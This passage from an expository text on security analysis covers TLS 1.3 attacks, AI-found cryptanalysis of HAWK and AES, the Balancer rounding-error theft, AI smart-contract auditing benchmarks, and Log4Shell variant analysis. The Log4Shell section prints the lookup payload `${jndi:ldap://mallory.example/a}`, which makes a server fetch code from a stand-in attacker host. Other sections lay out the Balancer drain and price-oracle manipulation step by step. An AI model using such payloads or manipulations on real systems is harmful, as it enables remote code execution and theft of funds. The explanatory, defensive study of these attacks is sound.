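This attack closely resembles Lowe's attack. Alice connects to Mallory's server, and Mallory connects to Ben's. When both connections later resume, Mallory relays enough messages to make the records of the two handshakes identical, even though the secret keys differ. Ben then asks the user to prove her identity. Mallory passes the request to Alice, who signs the record of her handshake with Mallory, and Ben accepts the signature because it also matches his own record. The designers prevented the attack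 by making the signature also cover later messages that depend on the secret keys.

Researchers used several methods to prove important properties of TLS 1.3. In 2019, Nir Drucker and Shay Gueron nevertheless found an attack, which they called Selfie, on connections that use a pre-shared key. In these connections, two computers authenticate each other with a secret they already share instead of with certificates.

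Suppose Alice's and Ben's computers share such a key, and each can both open connections and answer them. When Alice's computer tries to contact Ben's, Mallory sends the messages straight back, so Alice's computer answers its own request. Since it has the right key, every check succeeds, and it treats the connection as one to Ben's computer. If it is checking whether Ben's computer still has a backup of a file, it may receive a "yes" from itself and delete its only copy.

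The earlier proofs assumed that each pre-shared key belonged to one client and one server, so they did not cover a computer that acted as both. Using a different key for each direction prevents the attack, as does including both computers' identities when deriving the key.

### What people choose and what tools check

In these analyses, people chose the model, the attacker's abilities and the properties to verify, and a tool could check far more cases within those limits than a person could. The attack that Cremers and colleagues found involved several interleaved connections, which would be easy to overlook by hand. Selfie is a much simpler attack, but a tool could not have found it in a model where computers had fixed roles.

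Mistaken assumptions also affect the analysis of signature schemes. The specification of HAWK, a proposed scheme, claimed extra security properties and cited a published analysis as support. *Weak Keys Break the BUFF Security of HAWK* (Dao, 2026) refuted the claim. Several of those properties concern an attacker who chooses the public key she registers, and HAWK's reference software checked almost nothing about a key beyond whether it could be decoded.

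### Claude's attacks on HAWK and AES

Protocol verifiers assume that the underlying algorithms are secure. In July 2026, Anthropic's *Discovering cryptographic weaknesses with Claude* reported that Claude Mythos Preview had found better attacks on two such algorithms, HAWK and a reduced version of AES. These attacks exploit weaknesses in the algorithms' mathematics rather than flaws in protocols or programming errors such as those in wolfSSL.

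HAWK is a digital signature scheme meant to withstand quantum computers. It was one of nine candidates in the third round of a selection process run by NIST, the US standards agency, and the only one based on lattices, which are regular grids of points in many dimensions. The secret key is a matrix *B* describing such a grid. The public key is *Q* = *B*\**B*, where *B*\* is the conjugate transpose of *B*. It reveals the lengths of the secret vectors and the angles between them, but not directly the vectors themselves. An attacker who finds any matrix that gives the same *Q* can forge signatures.

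van Gent and Pulles (2025), in *HAWK*, had shown that someone who knew a certain kind of symmetry of the grid could reduce this to a problem of at most half the size. They didn't have a usable symmetry for HAWK itself. Straznickas and Weis, in *HAWK-n Key Recovery Reduces to SVP in Dimension n/2 + 1*, explain the one that Mythos found. The entries of *B* are built from a number ζ, and an operation τ replaces ζ with −ζ throughout. The attack looks for the matrix

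*V* = *B*⁻¹τ(*B*).

*V* depends on the secret key, but it is among the shortest solutions to equations that anyone can write down from the public key. The attacker recovers *V* with standard methods for finding short vectors, then uses van Gent and Pulles's procedure to turn it into a working key.

The table compares HAWK's previous security estimates with those of Straznickas and Weis. The estimates of attack effort for HAWK-256 instead come from Anthropic's announcement and use a different measure. "Dimension" is the size of the short-vector problems an attacker must solve.

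| Version | Dimension before | Dimension after | Cost before | Cost after |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| HAWK-256 | 211 | 129 | 2⁶⁴ | 2³⁸ |
| HAWK-512 | 452 | 257 | 2¹⁵⁰ | 2¹⁰⁸ |
| HAWK-1024 | 940 | 513 | 2²⁸⁸ | 2¹⁸² |

The attack cuts the dimension nearly in half for the larger versions, but it lowers the exponent of the computation required by 28% to 41%, less than the halving of key strength that Anthropic describes. Only HAWK-256, which the designers offered as a target for cryptanalysts and never proposed for use, is now practical to attack. According to The Hacker News (2026), recovering a HAWK-256 key takes about three hours and 42 minutes on a 96-core server.

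HAWK's designers confirmed the attack and withdrew the scheme the day after the announcement. Larger keys would restore its security but make it uncompetitive. NIST's *Round 3 Additional Signatures* now lists HAWK as withdrawn. *AI Broke a NIST Candidate. Not Your Encryption* (2026) reports that a separate team used GPT-5.6 to attack HAWK with a different mathematical approach.

The second result concerns AES, the standard cipher for encrypting data. AES-128 scrambles its input in ten rounds, and researchers study versions with fewer rounds to see how much security margin remains. The best earlier attack on seven rounds built a large table of intermediate values, then tried 256 possibilities for one unknown before each search of the table. Mythos found a quantity that is the same for all 256, so the attacker no longer has to guess the unknown. Anthropic estimates that the new attack is 200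 to 800 times faster, even with the extra calculation it requires.

The attack on reduced-round AES-128 is still impractical. It requires about 2¹⁰⁵ chosen messages encrypted under the victim's key, and collecting them at a trillion per second would take more than a trillion years. Neither result affects any production system, since HAWK was only a candidate and the full AES-128 uses ten rounds.

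### How much the model did alone

Each result cost about $100,000 in model usage. The HAWK attack took about 60 hours to find, develop and verify. A researcher who knew theoretical computer science but wasn't a lattice specialist advised the model on matters such as keeping track of ideas and choosing software. Two copies of the model investigated the crucial idea, and one made it work after the other had rejected it too early.

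The AES research needed more persistence from the researcher. Claude at first said there was nothing left to find in such a heavily studied cipher. The researcher told it that models tend to give up on the problem because they think it is impossible, and suggested attacking seven rounds. Over the next three days, the researcher sent three more substantive messages, none of which contained cryptographic ideas. In one of them, the researcher refused to let the model switch to an easier cipher. Anthropic is justified in calling the mathematical work largely autonomous, although a person chose the target and the standard of success.

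Anthropic contrasts the 60 hours with the two years of expert review that HAWK had survived. The comparison is a little unfair to the experts, because the model could start from van Gent and Pulles's 2025 result. But that result was public, and NIST had encouraged more work on the problem behind HAWK.

Matthew Green, a cryptographer, takes a similar view in *Some notes about Anthropic's new results* (Cryptography Engineering, 2026). He considers the HAWK result very meaningful because the scheme had a real chance of becoming a standard, but notes that the result combines well-known tools instead of inventing new mathematics. He finds the AES result much less interesting and isn't sure the claimed speedup is real, because nobody can run the attack.

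Anthropic tested parts of the AES attack separately and ran a complete version against a miniature cipher with a 24-bit key. The two researchers still needed nearly a month to become confident in the method. The HAWK attack was much easier to check, because anyone can run the code, sign a message with the recovered key, and see whether the ordinary verification software accepts it.

The same is true of a later attack that Anthropic has announced but not yet published in full. It targets 13 of the 24 rounds of a cipher called LEA and recovers a key in under an hour on a desktop computer, whereas the best previous attack required about 2⁸⁶ operations.

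In Cryptography Engineering, Green calls verification the new bottleneck, because models can produce real results but are even better at producing ones that only look real. He suggests that proofs in Lean, a language that lets a computer check each step, could help with results like the AES attack. An expert would often still have to check that the theorem states the right thing.

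## How an audited smart contract lost over 100 million dollars

On 3 November 2025, attackers stole more than 100 million dollars from Balancer, an exchange for digital currencies. At least three security companies had reviewed its code, and one of them had proved two theorems about the type of pool that the attackers emptied. Both proofs were valid, but neither theorem ruled out the theft.

### Pools and their prices

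Balancer consists of smart contracts, programs that hold money on a blockchain (a public ledger that many computers maintain together) and can pay it out without anyone's approval. Anyone can call a contract's public functions, and payments are hard to reverse. Each transaction either completes in full or has no effect, and no other transaction can interrupt it.

Users of Balancer trade against a liquidity pool, which is a shared reserve of two or more tokens. A formula sets the price. In the simplest kind of pool, the product of the two balances must stay the same:

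*x* × *y* = *k*.

Suppose a pool holds 100 ether and 400,000 dollar tokens, so *k* is 40 million. If Alice adds 1 ether, the pool keeps 40,000,000 / 101 ≈ 396,040 dollar tokens, and she receives the other 3,960.

Balancer's stable pools hold tokens of nearly equal value and use a more complicated formula. The formula combines the balances into one number, *D*, which represents the value of the whole pool. Programmers call *k* and *D* "invariants" because a trade should leave them unchanged, apart from fees. In software testing, an invariant is more broadly any condition that should hold in every state a program can reach.

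People who deposit money in a pool receive pool tokens, which represent shares in it. According to BlockSec's *In-Depth Analysis* (2025), the price of one pool token is about *D* / *S*, where *S* is the number of pool tokens in circulation. The attackers chose "composable" stable pools, where users could trade the pool tokens like any other token.

### Rounding 9.9 down to 9

Some tokens represent deposited ether that earns a return, so one of them might be worth 1.1 ether. Before using its formula, a pool multiplies each amount by the token's exchange rate to put the amounts on the same scale. Smart contracts on Ethereum calculate in whole numbers, and Balancer's code rounded the product down.

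If a trader asks for 9 units of the token, worth 9 × 1.1 = 9.9, the pool rounds the value down to 9 and charges that amount, so the trader gets about 9% of the purchase free. The pool should have rounded up, so that any error was in its favour.

The rounding loss hardly matters in an ordinary trade. It is always less than one unit, however large the trade, and most tokens divide into 10¹⁸ units, so a trader who wants nine whole tokens asks for 9 × 10¹⁸ units.

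| Units requested | Exchange rate | Exact result | Recorded result | Share lost |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 9 | 1.1 | 9.9 | 9 | 9.1% |
| 17 (from an actual attack) | 1.058 | 17.99 | 17 | 5.5% |
| 8 (from another attack) | 1.115 | 8.918 | 8 | 10.3% |
| 9 × 10¹⁸ | 1.1 | 9.9 × 10¹⁸ | 9.9 × 10¹⁸ | None |

The programmers knew about the rounding. They wrote in a code comment that the two sides of a swap needed different rounding, but that the impact "is expected to be minimal".

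### How a tiny error emptied the pools

To profit from the error, an attacker had to bring the balances down to a handful of units and then repeat the error many times. Balancer's batch function, which carries out a list of swaps in one transaction, made both possible. It settled accounts only at the end of the batch, so the attacker could sell pool tokens without owning any and buy them back later. Brener, Lo Buglio and colleagues (2025), of the auditing company OpenZeppelin, reconstructed one attack roughly as follows:

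1. Sell borrowed pool tokens for the pool's other tokens until about 100,000 units or fewer remain.
2. Swap again to leave exactly 18 units of one token.
3. Buy 17 of the 18 units, which triggers the rounding error and lowers *D*.
4. Swap back to restore the balances, then repeat from step 2.
5. Buy back the pool tokens, which are now cheap, and settle the debt.

In *How an Attacker Drained $128M from Balancer Through Rounding Error Exploitation*, Barda, Zaikin and Vanunu (2025) counted more than 65 small swaps. The balances during these swaps were worth far less than a cent, so the money came from the last step of the attack.

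In a simplified example, a pool holds assets worth $1,000 and has 1,000 pool tokens in circulation, each worth $1. The attacker borrows 990 pool tokens and sells them to the pool for $990 in assets, leaving $10 in the pool and 10 pool tokens in circulation. Repeated rounding then cuts *D* from 10 to 5, so a pool token costs 50 cents. The attacker buys 990 of them for $495, repays the loan and keeps $495. The $5 error has cost the depositors about half their money because it halved the price of every pool token.

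Estimates of the total loss range from over $100 million (Trail of Bits' *Balancer hack analysis and guidance for the DeFi ecosystem*) to $128.64 million (Barda and colleagues). Some of these totals include losses from other projects that had copied Balancer's code. BlockSec's *#3 Balancer V2 Incident* (2026) says that about $45 million was reportedly recovered. BlockSec also found that Balancer couldn't pause the affected contracts, which gave other people time to copy the attack.

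### What the auditors had reviewed

Three of the auditing companies published their own accounts after the theft. Each company has a reputation to protect, but the accounts are specific and broadly consistent.

| Date | Company | What it reviewed | Connection with the flaw |
|---|---|---|---|
| February–March 2021 | OpenZeppelin | The original pools and the batch function | The rounding was there but harmless |
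| April 2021 | Trail of Bits | An early version of Balancer v2 | The flaw was absent, but similar rounding errors were present |
| August–September 2021 | OpenZeppelin | Changes to the original stable pool | The vulnerable pool types were outside the scope |
| October 2021 | Trail of Bits | Linear pools, a related type | Trail of Bits reported the rounding problem |
| 2022 | Certora | Stable pools | Certora proved two properties that didn't exclude the flaw |
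| September 2022 | Trail of Bits | Composable stable pools, the type later attacked | The scope excluded the library for stable-pool mathematics |

The number of audits is uncertain. Trail of Bits says it conducted three reviews in 2021 but describes only two from that year, plus the one in 2022. Brener and colleagues count four auditing companies without naming them all. This suggests at least six reviews, and probably more.

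The rounding was harmless in the pools that OpenZeppelin audited because they multiplied amounts only by powers of ten, to allow for tokens with different numbers of decimal places. Multiplying by a whole number leaves nothing to round. The code comment included a warning that "there's no rounding error unless `_scalingFactor()` is overriden". Balancer's programmers later overrode that function to include exchange rates, first in one pool type in July 2021 and then in the composable pools that September.

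Brener and colleagues say that the vulnerable code appeared after OpenZeppelin's audit, but their own timeline puts the July change five weeks before the second audit began. OpenZeppelin's better defence is that Balancer hadn't asked it to review those pools.

Trail of Bits came closest to preventing the theft. In October 2021 it reported the rounding problem in linear pools as finding TOB-BALANCER-004. It rated the severity "undetermined" because it couldn't tell whether anyone could exploit the problem in those pools. It recommended extensive fuzzing to check the direction of every rounding operation. Trail of Bits now says the attackers used the same vulnerability in the composable pools.

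When Trail of Bits reviewed those pools a year later, the mathematics library was out of scope. That only partly explains why the review missed the error, because BlockSec locates the incorrect rounding in the pool's own swap code, before it calls the library. The damage becomes visible only when the library calculates *D*.

Auditors' expectations also mattered. Trail of Bits recalls that the industry didn't regard arithmetic errors as a major risk in 2021, when the largest thefts came from stolen keys and faulty access control. Rounding attacks became common only later, including one that emptied the lending project Hundred Finance in 2023. Trail of Bits has since tightened its standards and would now rate arithmetic like that of the linear pools as "Weak" instead of "Moderate".

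### The properties Certora proved

Certora's *Breaking Down the Balancer Hack* (2025) describes the two properties that it had proved in 2022:

- The users' pool tokens never add up to more than the total supply.
- Nobody can create new pool tokens without adding assets to the pool.

Both properties still hold in the simplified attack above. The attacker doesn't create pool tokens from nothing, and does pay for the 990 tokens at the end. But the price is wrong because the attacker changed it, and neither property covers the price. Similarly, the proof of the Wi-Fi handshake that existed before KRACK didn't cover what those attackers changed.

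With hindsight, Certora identified two more invariants that would have exposed the flaw. One concerns a round trip. If a trader swaps an amount *x* of one token for another, swaps everything back, and ends with *x*′, then

*x*′ ≤ *x*.

The other says that no operation may reduce the value of a pool token. If *D* and *S* become *D*′ and *S*′, then

*D*′ / *S*′ ≥ *D* / *S*.

In the simplified attack this ratio falls from 1 to 0.5, so the rounding step violates the rule.

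Once someone has written down an invariant, a fuzzer such as Trail of Bits' Echidna can run many sequences of transactions and report any that violate it. The fuzzer can find bugs that don't cause a crash, because it uses the invariant to decide whether a test has failed. But it may never try a pool with only 18 units left unless the tester sets very small starting balances.

A prover covers every possible value, including tiny ones, but does not always handle complicated arithmetic well. Certora had replaced parts of the stable-pool mathematics with simpler approximations, and acknowledges that this can hide small rounding errors. For Balancer v3, the next version, Certora proved the round-trip rule for a simplified pool and used ordinary tests where a full proof was too difficult.

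Some invariants apply to more than one project. Any exchange should satisfy the round-trip rule, and Certora says it routinely checks similar invariants in other projects. Trail of Bits says the more familiar rule that "rounding must favor the protocol" is too vague because it misses cases that arise over several operations. An expert therefore has to work out what the rule requires of each calculation, and preferably write it down while the software is still being designed.

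An expert may also have to judge how serious a violation is. If a fuzzer reports that a trader can gain one unit, worth a tiny fraction of a cent, the expert has to work out whether an attacker could turn this into a large profit. Trail of Bits faced this question in 2021 and did not resolve it.

### The 80% estimate

*Demystifying Exploitable Bugs in Smart Contracts* (Zhang, Zhang and colleagues, 2023) used 516 vulnerabilities from 2021 and 2022 to estimate how many such flaws automated tools could find. Of these, 462 came from Code4rena, a platform where independent auditors compete for rewards by finding faults in a project before its launch. The other 54 came from reports on deployed contracts, including thefts and cases where a researcher warned the owners first. Excluding some kinds of vulnerability, such as those that needed an insider or a deceived user, left 385.

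They then read the literature on 37 detection methods and listed 17 types of bug that at least one could find. A vulnerability of any of these types counted as "machine auditable", on the assumption that every tool worked perfectly. By this generous standard, tools could find only 20.5% of the vulnerabilities, leaving 79.5% beyond them. Zhang and colleagues sorted the remaining 306 into seven categories:

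| Category | What goes wrong | Audit contests | Deployed contracts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Erroneous accounting | A financial formula is incorrect | 72 | 3 |
| Inconsistent state updates | The code changes one value but not another that depends on it | 49 | 4 |
| Implementation-specific | The error is peculiar to one contract | 44 | 5 |
| ID uniqueness violation | Two users or assets can have the same identifier | 43 | 1 |
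| Privilege escalation | An unexpected sequence of actions avoids an access check | 25 | 8 |
| Atomicity violation | Two processes interfere with each other | 22 | 2 |
| Price-oracle manipulation | An attacker distorts a price that the contract relies on | 16 | 12 |

The 80% figure describes the tools of 2022 and the bugs that were left for auditors to find. Zhang and colleagues point out that developers may already have used tools to remove many simpler bugs. *On the Shoulders of Giants* (2026) adds that contests encourage auditors to skip bugs that a machine can easily detect, since a finding that many people report earns less. Both effects would make tools look worse than they are. *Smart Contract Vulnerabilities, Tools, and Benchmarks* (2024), a literature review, takes the figure from the same study, so it isn't independent support.

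The criterion can also make tools look better than they are. "Precision loss" is one of the 17 machine-auditable types, so the Balancer flaw would arguably count among the 20% that tools could find, even though a tool that detects some precision errors won't necessarily find this one.

*What are the Actual Flaws in Important Smart Contracts* (2019) gives a lower estimate for a different question, concluding that even much better tools, supplied with handwritten correctness properties, would probably miss 35% of the most serious audit findings. The samples differ, but it makes sense that the estimate falls when people can tell the tools what to check. Zhang and colleagues likewise thought that five of their seven categories, with about 60% of the bugs, were regular enough for someone to devise general test oracles.

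Human auditors weren't reliable either. In the contests, 54% of the bugs that tools couldn't find were each reported by only one auditor, and the proportion was almost the same for the bugs that tools could find. Many of these bugs could easily have gone unnoticed if the auditor who reported them hadn't entered.

### Price-oracle manipulation

A price oracle is a source that a contract uses to get an asset's price (it is unrelated to test oracles). Price-oracle manipulation was the most common category among the deployed contracts but the least common in the contests. Zhang and colleagues consider it the hardest to audit, with a single auditor reporting 75% of the cases found in contests.

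Suppose a lending contract calculates the price of ether from the balances of the pool in the first example, which holds 100 ether and 400,000 dollar tokens. It divides one balance by the other and gets $4,000. Ben has borrowed $100,000 against 100 ether. If his debt exceeds 80% of the value of his ether, anyone may pay it off and take the ether. At $4,000 he is quite safe. Mallory then does the following in one transaction:

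1. She sells 100 ether to the pool for 200,000 dollar tokens. The pool now holds 200 of one and 200,000 of the other, so the contract calculates a price of $1,000.
2. Ben's ether now appears to be worth $100,000, and 80% of that is less than his debt. Mallory pays his $100,000 debt and receives his 100 ether, which are really worth $400,000.
3. She buys back her original 100 ether from the pool for 200,000 dollar tokens.

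Ignoring fees, she makes $300,000. Everything happens within one transaction, so no other trader can correct the price between steps. Zhang and colleagues adapted the example from an attack on Deus Finance that caused a loss of $3.1 million.

The pool followed its formula throughout, and the lending contract correctly divided one balance by the other. The lending contract's programmers assumed this ratio was the market price, which is usually true. A common fix is to use an average price over a longer period, so a distortion within one transaction has no effect. As with Balancer, an auditor has to imagine someone deliberately putting a pool into a state that ordinary trading would never produce.

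### EVMbench

Language models are a newer and different kind of tool. In February 2026 OpenAI released EVMbench with the investment firm Paradigm and the security company OtterSec. It tests AI agents on 120 serious vulnerabilities (117 in OpenAI's announcement), mostly from Code4rena contests. The agents must detect vulnerabilities, repair them, or exploit them to steal funds on a simulated blockchain. The best agent detected 45.6% of the vulnerabilities, and the best score for exploitation was 72.2%, on a smaller selection.

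Agents did better at exploiting vulnerabilities than at finding them. OpenAI's *Introducing EVMbench* (2026) suggests that this is because exploitation has an explicit goal, which is to keep trying until the funds are drained. An agent can check its balance after every attempt, and an increase shows progress. This check is almost as convenient an oracle as a crash. A gain alone wouldn't prove that a contract was faulty, since honest traders also make profits, but the exploitation tasks use only contracts with known vulnerabilities.

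An agent looking for vulnerabilities has no such signal, and OpenAI reports that some agents stopped after finding one vulnerability. The benchmark's grader measures recall by comparing an agent's report with what human auditors found. It doesn't measure the number of false positives, because an additional finding could be a real vulnerability that the auditors missed.

OpenZeppelin (2026) objected that most of the audit reports were public before the developers finished training the models, so the models may have remembered some answers. It also judged that at least four of the "high severity" vulnerabilities can't be exploited. One relies on a subtraction producing a huge number when the result should be negative, but the version of the programming language used cancels the transaction instead.

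The second objection is probably less serious than it sounds. Four vulnerabilities out of 120 can change a detection score by only about three percentage points, though that could still alter a close ranking. All four come from a small group of tasks based on a blockchain called Tempo, so they are weak evidence about the quality of the contest findings.

Peng, Wu and Zhou (2026), in *Re-Evaluating EVMBench*, repeated the original tests with more combinations of models and software. The best scores were 47.5% for detection and 61.1% for exploitation. To address the problem of remembered answers, they also tested some of the agents on 22 real thefts that took place after the release of every model in the study. Claude Opus 4.6 detected 13 of the 20 cases that they could grade (65%), but no agent made a profit in 110 attempts at exploitation.

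The 65% result makes it less likely that memory explains most of the original detection score, though the two sets differ in other ways, such as each theft involving a single flaw that someone had already exploited. The exploitation tasks were also harder than EVMbench's, because the agents had to work with a copy of the real blockchain and set up everything the attack needed. The agents mostly read code and queried balances without settling on a plan, so a clear measure of success wasn't enough when the attack required many coordinated steps.

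One of the original tasks included a flaw in a project called Abracadabra, whose code rounded down instead of up. None of the 26 combinations found it. This is the closest test of whether these agents would have caught Balancer's error, but it is only one case.

Peng and colleagues conclude that agents can't replace human judgement. Their employer and partner, BlockSec, sells audits, as does OpenZeppelin, so both have reason to welcome that conclusion. They ran their tests between 28 February and 8 March 2026, before the release of newer models such as Claude Opus 5.

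### Heimdallr's 92.45%

In *An Effective and Cost-Efficient Agentic Framework for Ethereum Smart Contract Auditing*, Hu, Chan and colleagues (2026) report a much higher figure, a detection rate of 92.45% on 30 contests from another platform, Sherlock. Their system, Heimdallr, divides a project into groups of related functions, asks a language model to look for vulnerabilities in each group, and then tries to filter out false positives.

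They obtained this result with the filter switched off, when 76.82% of the reports were false. With the filter on, Heimdallr detected 78.92%, and 47.36% of its reports were false. For every 100 real vulnerabilities, and counting one report for each, the two settings would produce roughly:

| Setting | Real vulnerabilities found | False reports |
|---|---|---|
| With the filter | 79 | 71 |
| Without the filter | 92 | 306 |

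Someone would have to check about 235 more false reports to gain 13 or 14 real vulnerabilities. The filtered figure describes the system more fairly and is still well above EVMbench's 45.6%. But the contests were different, and Hu and colleagues matched reports to known vulnerabilities by category and location in the code, so a match doesn't establish that the system understood the attack.

Here too, the answers may have been in the model's training data. The contests date from 2025 onwards, and the best results came from Claude Sonnet 4.5, which Anthropic released in September 2025. Heimdallr can also search the web and consult a library of published vulnerability reports, either of which might contain the answers.

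Hu and colleagues tested Heimdallr on 20 large thefts since June 2025, and it reconstructed 17 of them. They say that none of their models could have learned about these incidents in training, because the newest was Gemini 2.5 Pro. But the model they relied on most, Claude Sonnet 4.5, is newer, so the claim doesn't hold for it. The four previously unknown vulnerabilities that Heimdallr found in live projects are better evidence, because the models couldn't have learned about them from published reports.

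## Log4Shell and the search for variants of a known vulnerability

Trail of Bits had reported Balancer's rounding error in one type of pool four years before attackers used it in another. A variant is a vulnerability with the same cause as a known one, and searching for variants is called variant analysis. Attackers do it too, often starting from the patch for the original vulnerability. In December 2021, researchers searched very publicly for variants in Log4j, a Java logging library. Its developers released a fix for one vulnerability on 10 December, and by the 28th they had three more to fix.

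### How a log message could run code

Most programs keep a log, a running record of events such as logins and errors. Log4j is a free library for writing logs, and developers have built it into thousands of software packages. It can also replace certain expressions, called lookups, with the details they refer to. For example, it replaces `${java:version}` with the version of Java in use.

Some lookups use JNDI (Java Naming and Directory Interface), which fetches stored objects by name. The name can include the address of another computer, which JNDI may contact through a protocol called LDAP. Log4j expanded lookups in the text it was logging as well as in its own settings, so an attack on a website could go as follows:

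1. Mallory visits the site. In the field where her browser normally gives its name, she sends `${jndi:ldap://mallory.example/a}`.
2. The site logs the browser's name, as many sites do.
3. Log4j finds the lookup and passes the address to JNDI.
4. JNDI contacts Mallory's server, which directs it to a piece of Java code.
5. Java loads the code and runs it inside the site's own program.

This is Log4Shell, or CVE-2021-44228. It scored 10.0 out of 10 for severity, because Mallory needs no account and no help from a victim.

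Each of these five steps works as designed. The site records what it received, Log4j expands a lookup, and JNDI fetches the requested object. Code that correctly implements this design is still vulnerable, so Log4Shell is a design flaw. The design mixed data with control instructions, much as the Windows Metafile format did by allowing pictures to contain code.

The Cyber Safety Review Board, a US government advisory panel, traces the feature to July 2013 in its *Review of the December 2021 Log4j Event* (2022). A member of the open-source community requested JNDI lookups and supplied the code, which the volunteers who maintain Log4j reviewed and accepted on 18 July. They were presumably checking whether the feature worked, not how an attacker could use it.

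The vulnerability existed for more than eight years before anyone reported it. On 24 November 2021, Chen Zhaojun of Alibaba's cloud security team reported it to the Apache Software Foundation, which supports Log4j, with a description, a pointer to the vulnerable code and a working attack. This detail suggests that Chen read the code closely, although it doesn't prove that Chen found the flaw that way.

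Apache's developers then worked on the fix in public, as open-source projects usually do. Anyone could read the proposed changes from 29 November, and one was titled "Restrict LDAP access via JNDI". On 9 December a Chinese security company, BoundaryX, posted a partly redacted picture of an attack, and Apache brought its release forward to the next day. The Cyber Safety Review Board thought it likely that someone had worked out the vulnerability from the unreleased fix, but couldn't confirm this.

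### Four fixes in eighteen days

Apache's security page describes the vulnerabilities and what each release changed.

| Vulnerability | Made public | What an attacker could do | The fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2021-44228 (Log4Shell) | 10 December | Run code by getting a lookup into a log message | 2.15.0 turned off lookups in messages and limited JNDI to the local computer, both by default |
| CVE-2021-45046 | 14 December | Run code by putting the lookup in other logged data | 2.16.0 removed lookups in messages and turned off JNDI by default |
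| CVE-2021-45105 | 18 December | Crash the program with a lookup that refers to itself | 2.17.0 stopped expanding nested lookups outside the configuration |
| CVE-2021-44832 | 28 December | Run code after editing the logging configuration | 2.17.1 stopped database settings from using JNDI to reach other computers |

The first fix covered only hostile text in the log message itself. But an administrator can also have details added to every line of a program's log, such as the current user's login name, by putting `$${ctx:loginId}` in Log4j's configuration. Log4j inserted the name and then expanded any lookup it contained, so Mallory could try logging in under the name `${jndi:ldap://mallory.example/a}`.

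Limiting JNDI to the local computer should have made the second vulnerability fairly harmless, and Apache at first scored it 3.7 as a denial-of-service flaw. Researchers then found ways around the limit and ran code on several operating systems, so Apache raised the score to 9.0.

Release 2.16.0 restricted JNDI further but still expanded lookups inside logged data. If an attacker's login name is `${ctx:loginId}`, Log4j replaces it with the login name, which is the same string, and repeats this until the program runs out of memory for tracking the replacements. At least three researchers found this flaw independently.

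The last of the four is a borderline case. Log4j can write its log to a database and could use JNDI to find that database, so anyone able to edit the configuration could direct Log4j to a hostile server. Apache tells researchers on its page that it doesn't count reports that assume this kind of access as vulnerabilities, but it lists this one there with a moderate rating and a note that nobody will receive credit for it.

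Apache also had to withdraw some of its early advice. It had told people who couldn't upgrade to disable lookups in messages through a setting, but some logging functions, including `Logger.printf`, could still expand those lookups. Another workaround was to delete the JNDI lookup code from the library. Apache says this removes only one of the "two bugs" in Log4Shell, because Log4j would still expand other lookups in untrusted text and might reveal private data to anyone who can read the log.

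The repeated upgrades took a lot of time. One US federal department told the Cyber Safety Review Board it had spent 33,000 hours on its response. The board expected vulnerable copies to remain in use for a decade or longer. That seems about right so far, since Log4j was third on Cisco Talos's chart of the vulnerabilities attackers targeted most in 2025.

### Variant analysis, worked on Log4j

Stone (2022), of Project Zero, Google's team for finding serious vulnerabilities, recommends four kinds of analysis after someone reports a vulnerability. Root cause analysis identifies the underlying flaw that made the attack possible. Variant analysis looks for similar vulnerabilities, and patch analysis checks whether the proposed fix removes the root cause. Both usually require knowing the root cause. Exploit technique analysis examines what the vulnerability lets an attacker do and how attackers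 use it.

For Log4Shell, "an attacker can put `jndi` in a message" describes the attack. A better statement of the root cause is that text from outside the program can reach a function that acts on it. An auditor can turn this into a search with a tool such as CodeQL, which lets its user query code much as one would query a database. In plain English instead of CodeQL's own language, a first query might be:

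```
find   text, call
where  text is a message that a program gives Log4j to record
  and  call asks JNDI to look up a name
  and  text can flow into that name
```

The CodeQL query specifies a source, where untrusted text enters, and a sink, where that text can do damage. CodeQL is much better suited to Log4Shell than to missing access checks, where it did badly, because Log4Shell has a path from one identifiable piece of code to another.

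The first query describes only the original vulnerability. To find variants, the auditor relaxes one condition at a time:

| What the auditor changes | The new question | What it could have found |
|---|---|---|
| The source: any data in a log entry, not only the message | What else that a stranger controls can reach JNDI? | CVE-2021-45046 |
| The sink: any lookup, not only JNDI | What else can a lookup in a stranger's text do? | CVE-2021-45105, and leaks of private data |
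| The source again: Log4j's configuration | What else gives JNDI an address? | CVE-2021-44832 |

Log4j 1, an older version, has no lookups but can use JNDI if configured to. Researchers also reported a vulnerability in it, CVE-2021-4104.

The auditor then triages the hits to decide which are real. If the third query returns twelve places where Log4j passes a name from its configuration to JNDI, the auditor has to determine who can set each name and whether the owner intended them to have that power. Apache's awkward treatment of CVE-2021-44832 shows that even the people responsible for the software may not have a clear answer. After triage, the auditor fixes the real cases, reruns the queries on the repaired code, and tries them on other libraries. The search becomes less worthwhile as the query conditions get looser and more of the hits are false positives.

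The table makes choosing what to relax look easier than it was, because the answers are now known. The queries could also miss variants, because a static analyser can lose track of the text where Log4j stores a login name in one place and reads it back in another, or where it chooses a lookup at run time based on the word before the colon. The auditor might have to specify those connections, which takes some knowledge of how Log4j works.

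### Giving a fuzzer the missing oracle

A fuzzer that detects only crashes could have sent Log4j random text for years without finding Log4Shell, because the vulnerability causes a remote lookup rather than a crash. In December 2021 Google (2021) announced that the security company Code Intelligence had extended its Java fuzzer, Jazzer, to detect remote JNDI lookups. Google paid the company $25,000 for the work and arranged for continuous fuzzing of Log4j through OSS-Fuzz, its free service for open-source projects. By then, OSS-Fuzz had found more than 7,000 vulnerabilities in over 500 projects.

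The slides *Fuzzing Java with Jazzer* (2022) show the new detector rediscovering Log4Shell. The test program is a few lines long and passes whatever text the fuzzer generates to Log4j's error-logging function. In the log on the slides, the detector reports the flaw after roughly 9,800 inputs, at about 2,450 a second, so the search seems to have taken around four seconds.

According to the slides, the fuzzer needed both the detector and an improvement in how it monitors searches of a map, which is a table of names and values. Log4j probably uses such a table to find the right lookup, and a fuzzer is unlikely to produce the word `jndi` by chance. Jazzer found the vulnerability only when testing Log4j directly, not when testing a program that uses it. People also chose the detector's rule after learning from Chen's report what to look for. But with that rule, Jazzer can look for the same fault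 in any Java library without further help from an expert.

The self-referring lookup in CVE-2021-45105 needed no new detector, because it ends in an error that stops the program. But a fuzzer running the test on the slides would not have triggered that error, because the test logs only a message and the fault requires a configuration that inserts other data.

### How many exploited vulnerabilities are variants

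A zero-day is a vulnerability that attackers use before a fix is available. Google keeps a record of zero-days detected in use, and for some years it has counted how many were variants of vulnerabilities already public. The figures come from Stone's *A Year in Review of 0-days Exploited In-The-Wild in 2020* (2021), her report on the first half of 2022, and Google's *The Ups and Downs of 0-days* (2023).

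| Period | Zero-days detected in use | Variants | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2020 | 24 | 6 | 25% |
| 1 January to 15 June 2022 | 18 | At least 9 | At least 50% |
| All of 2022 | 41 | 17 | 41% |

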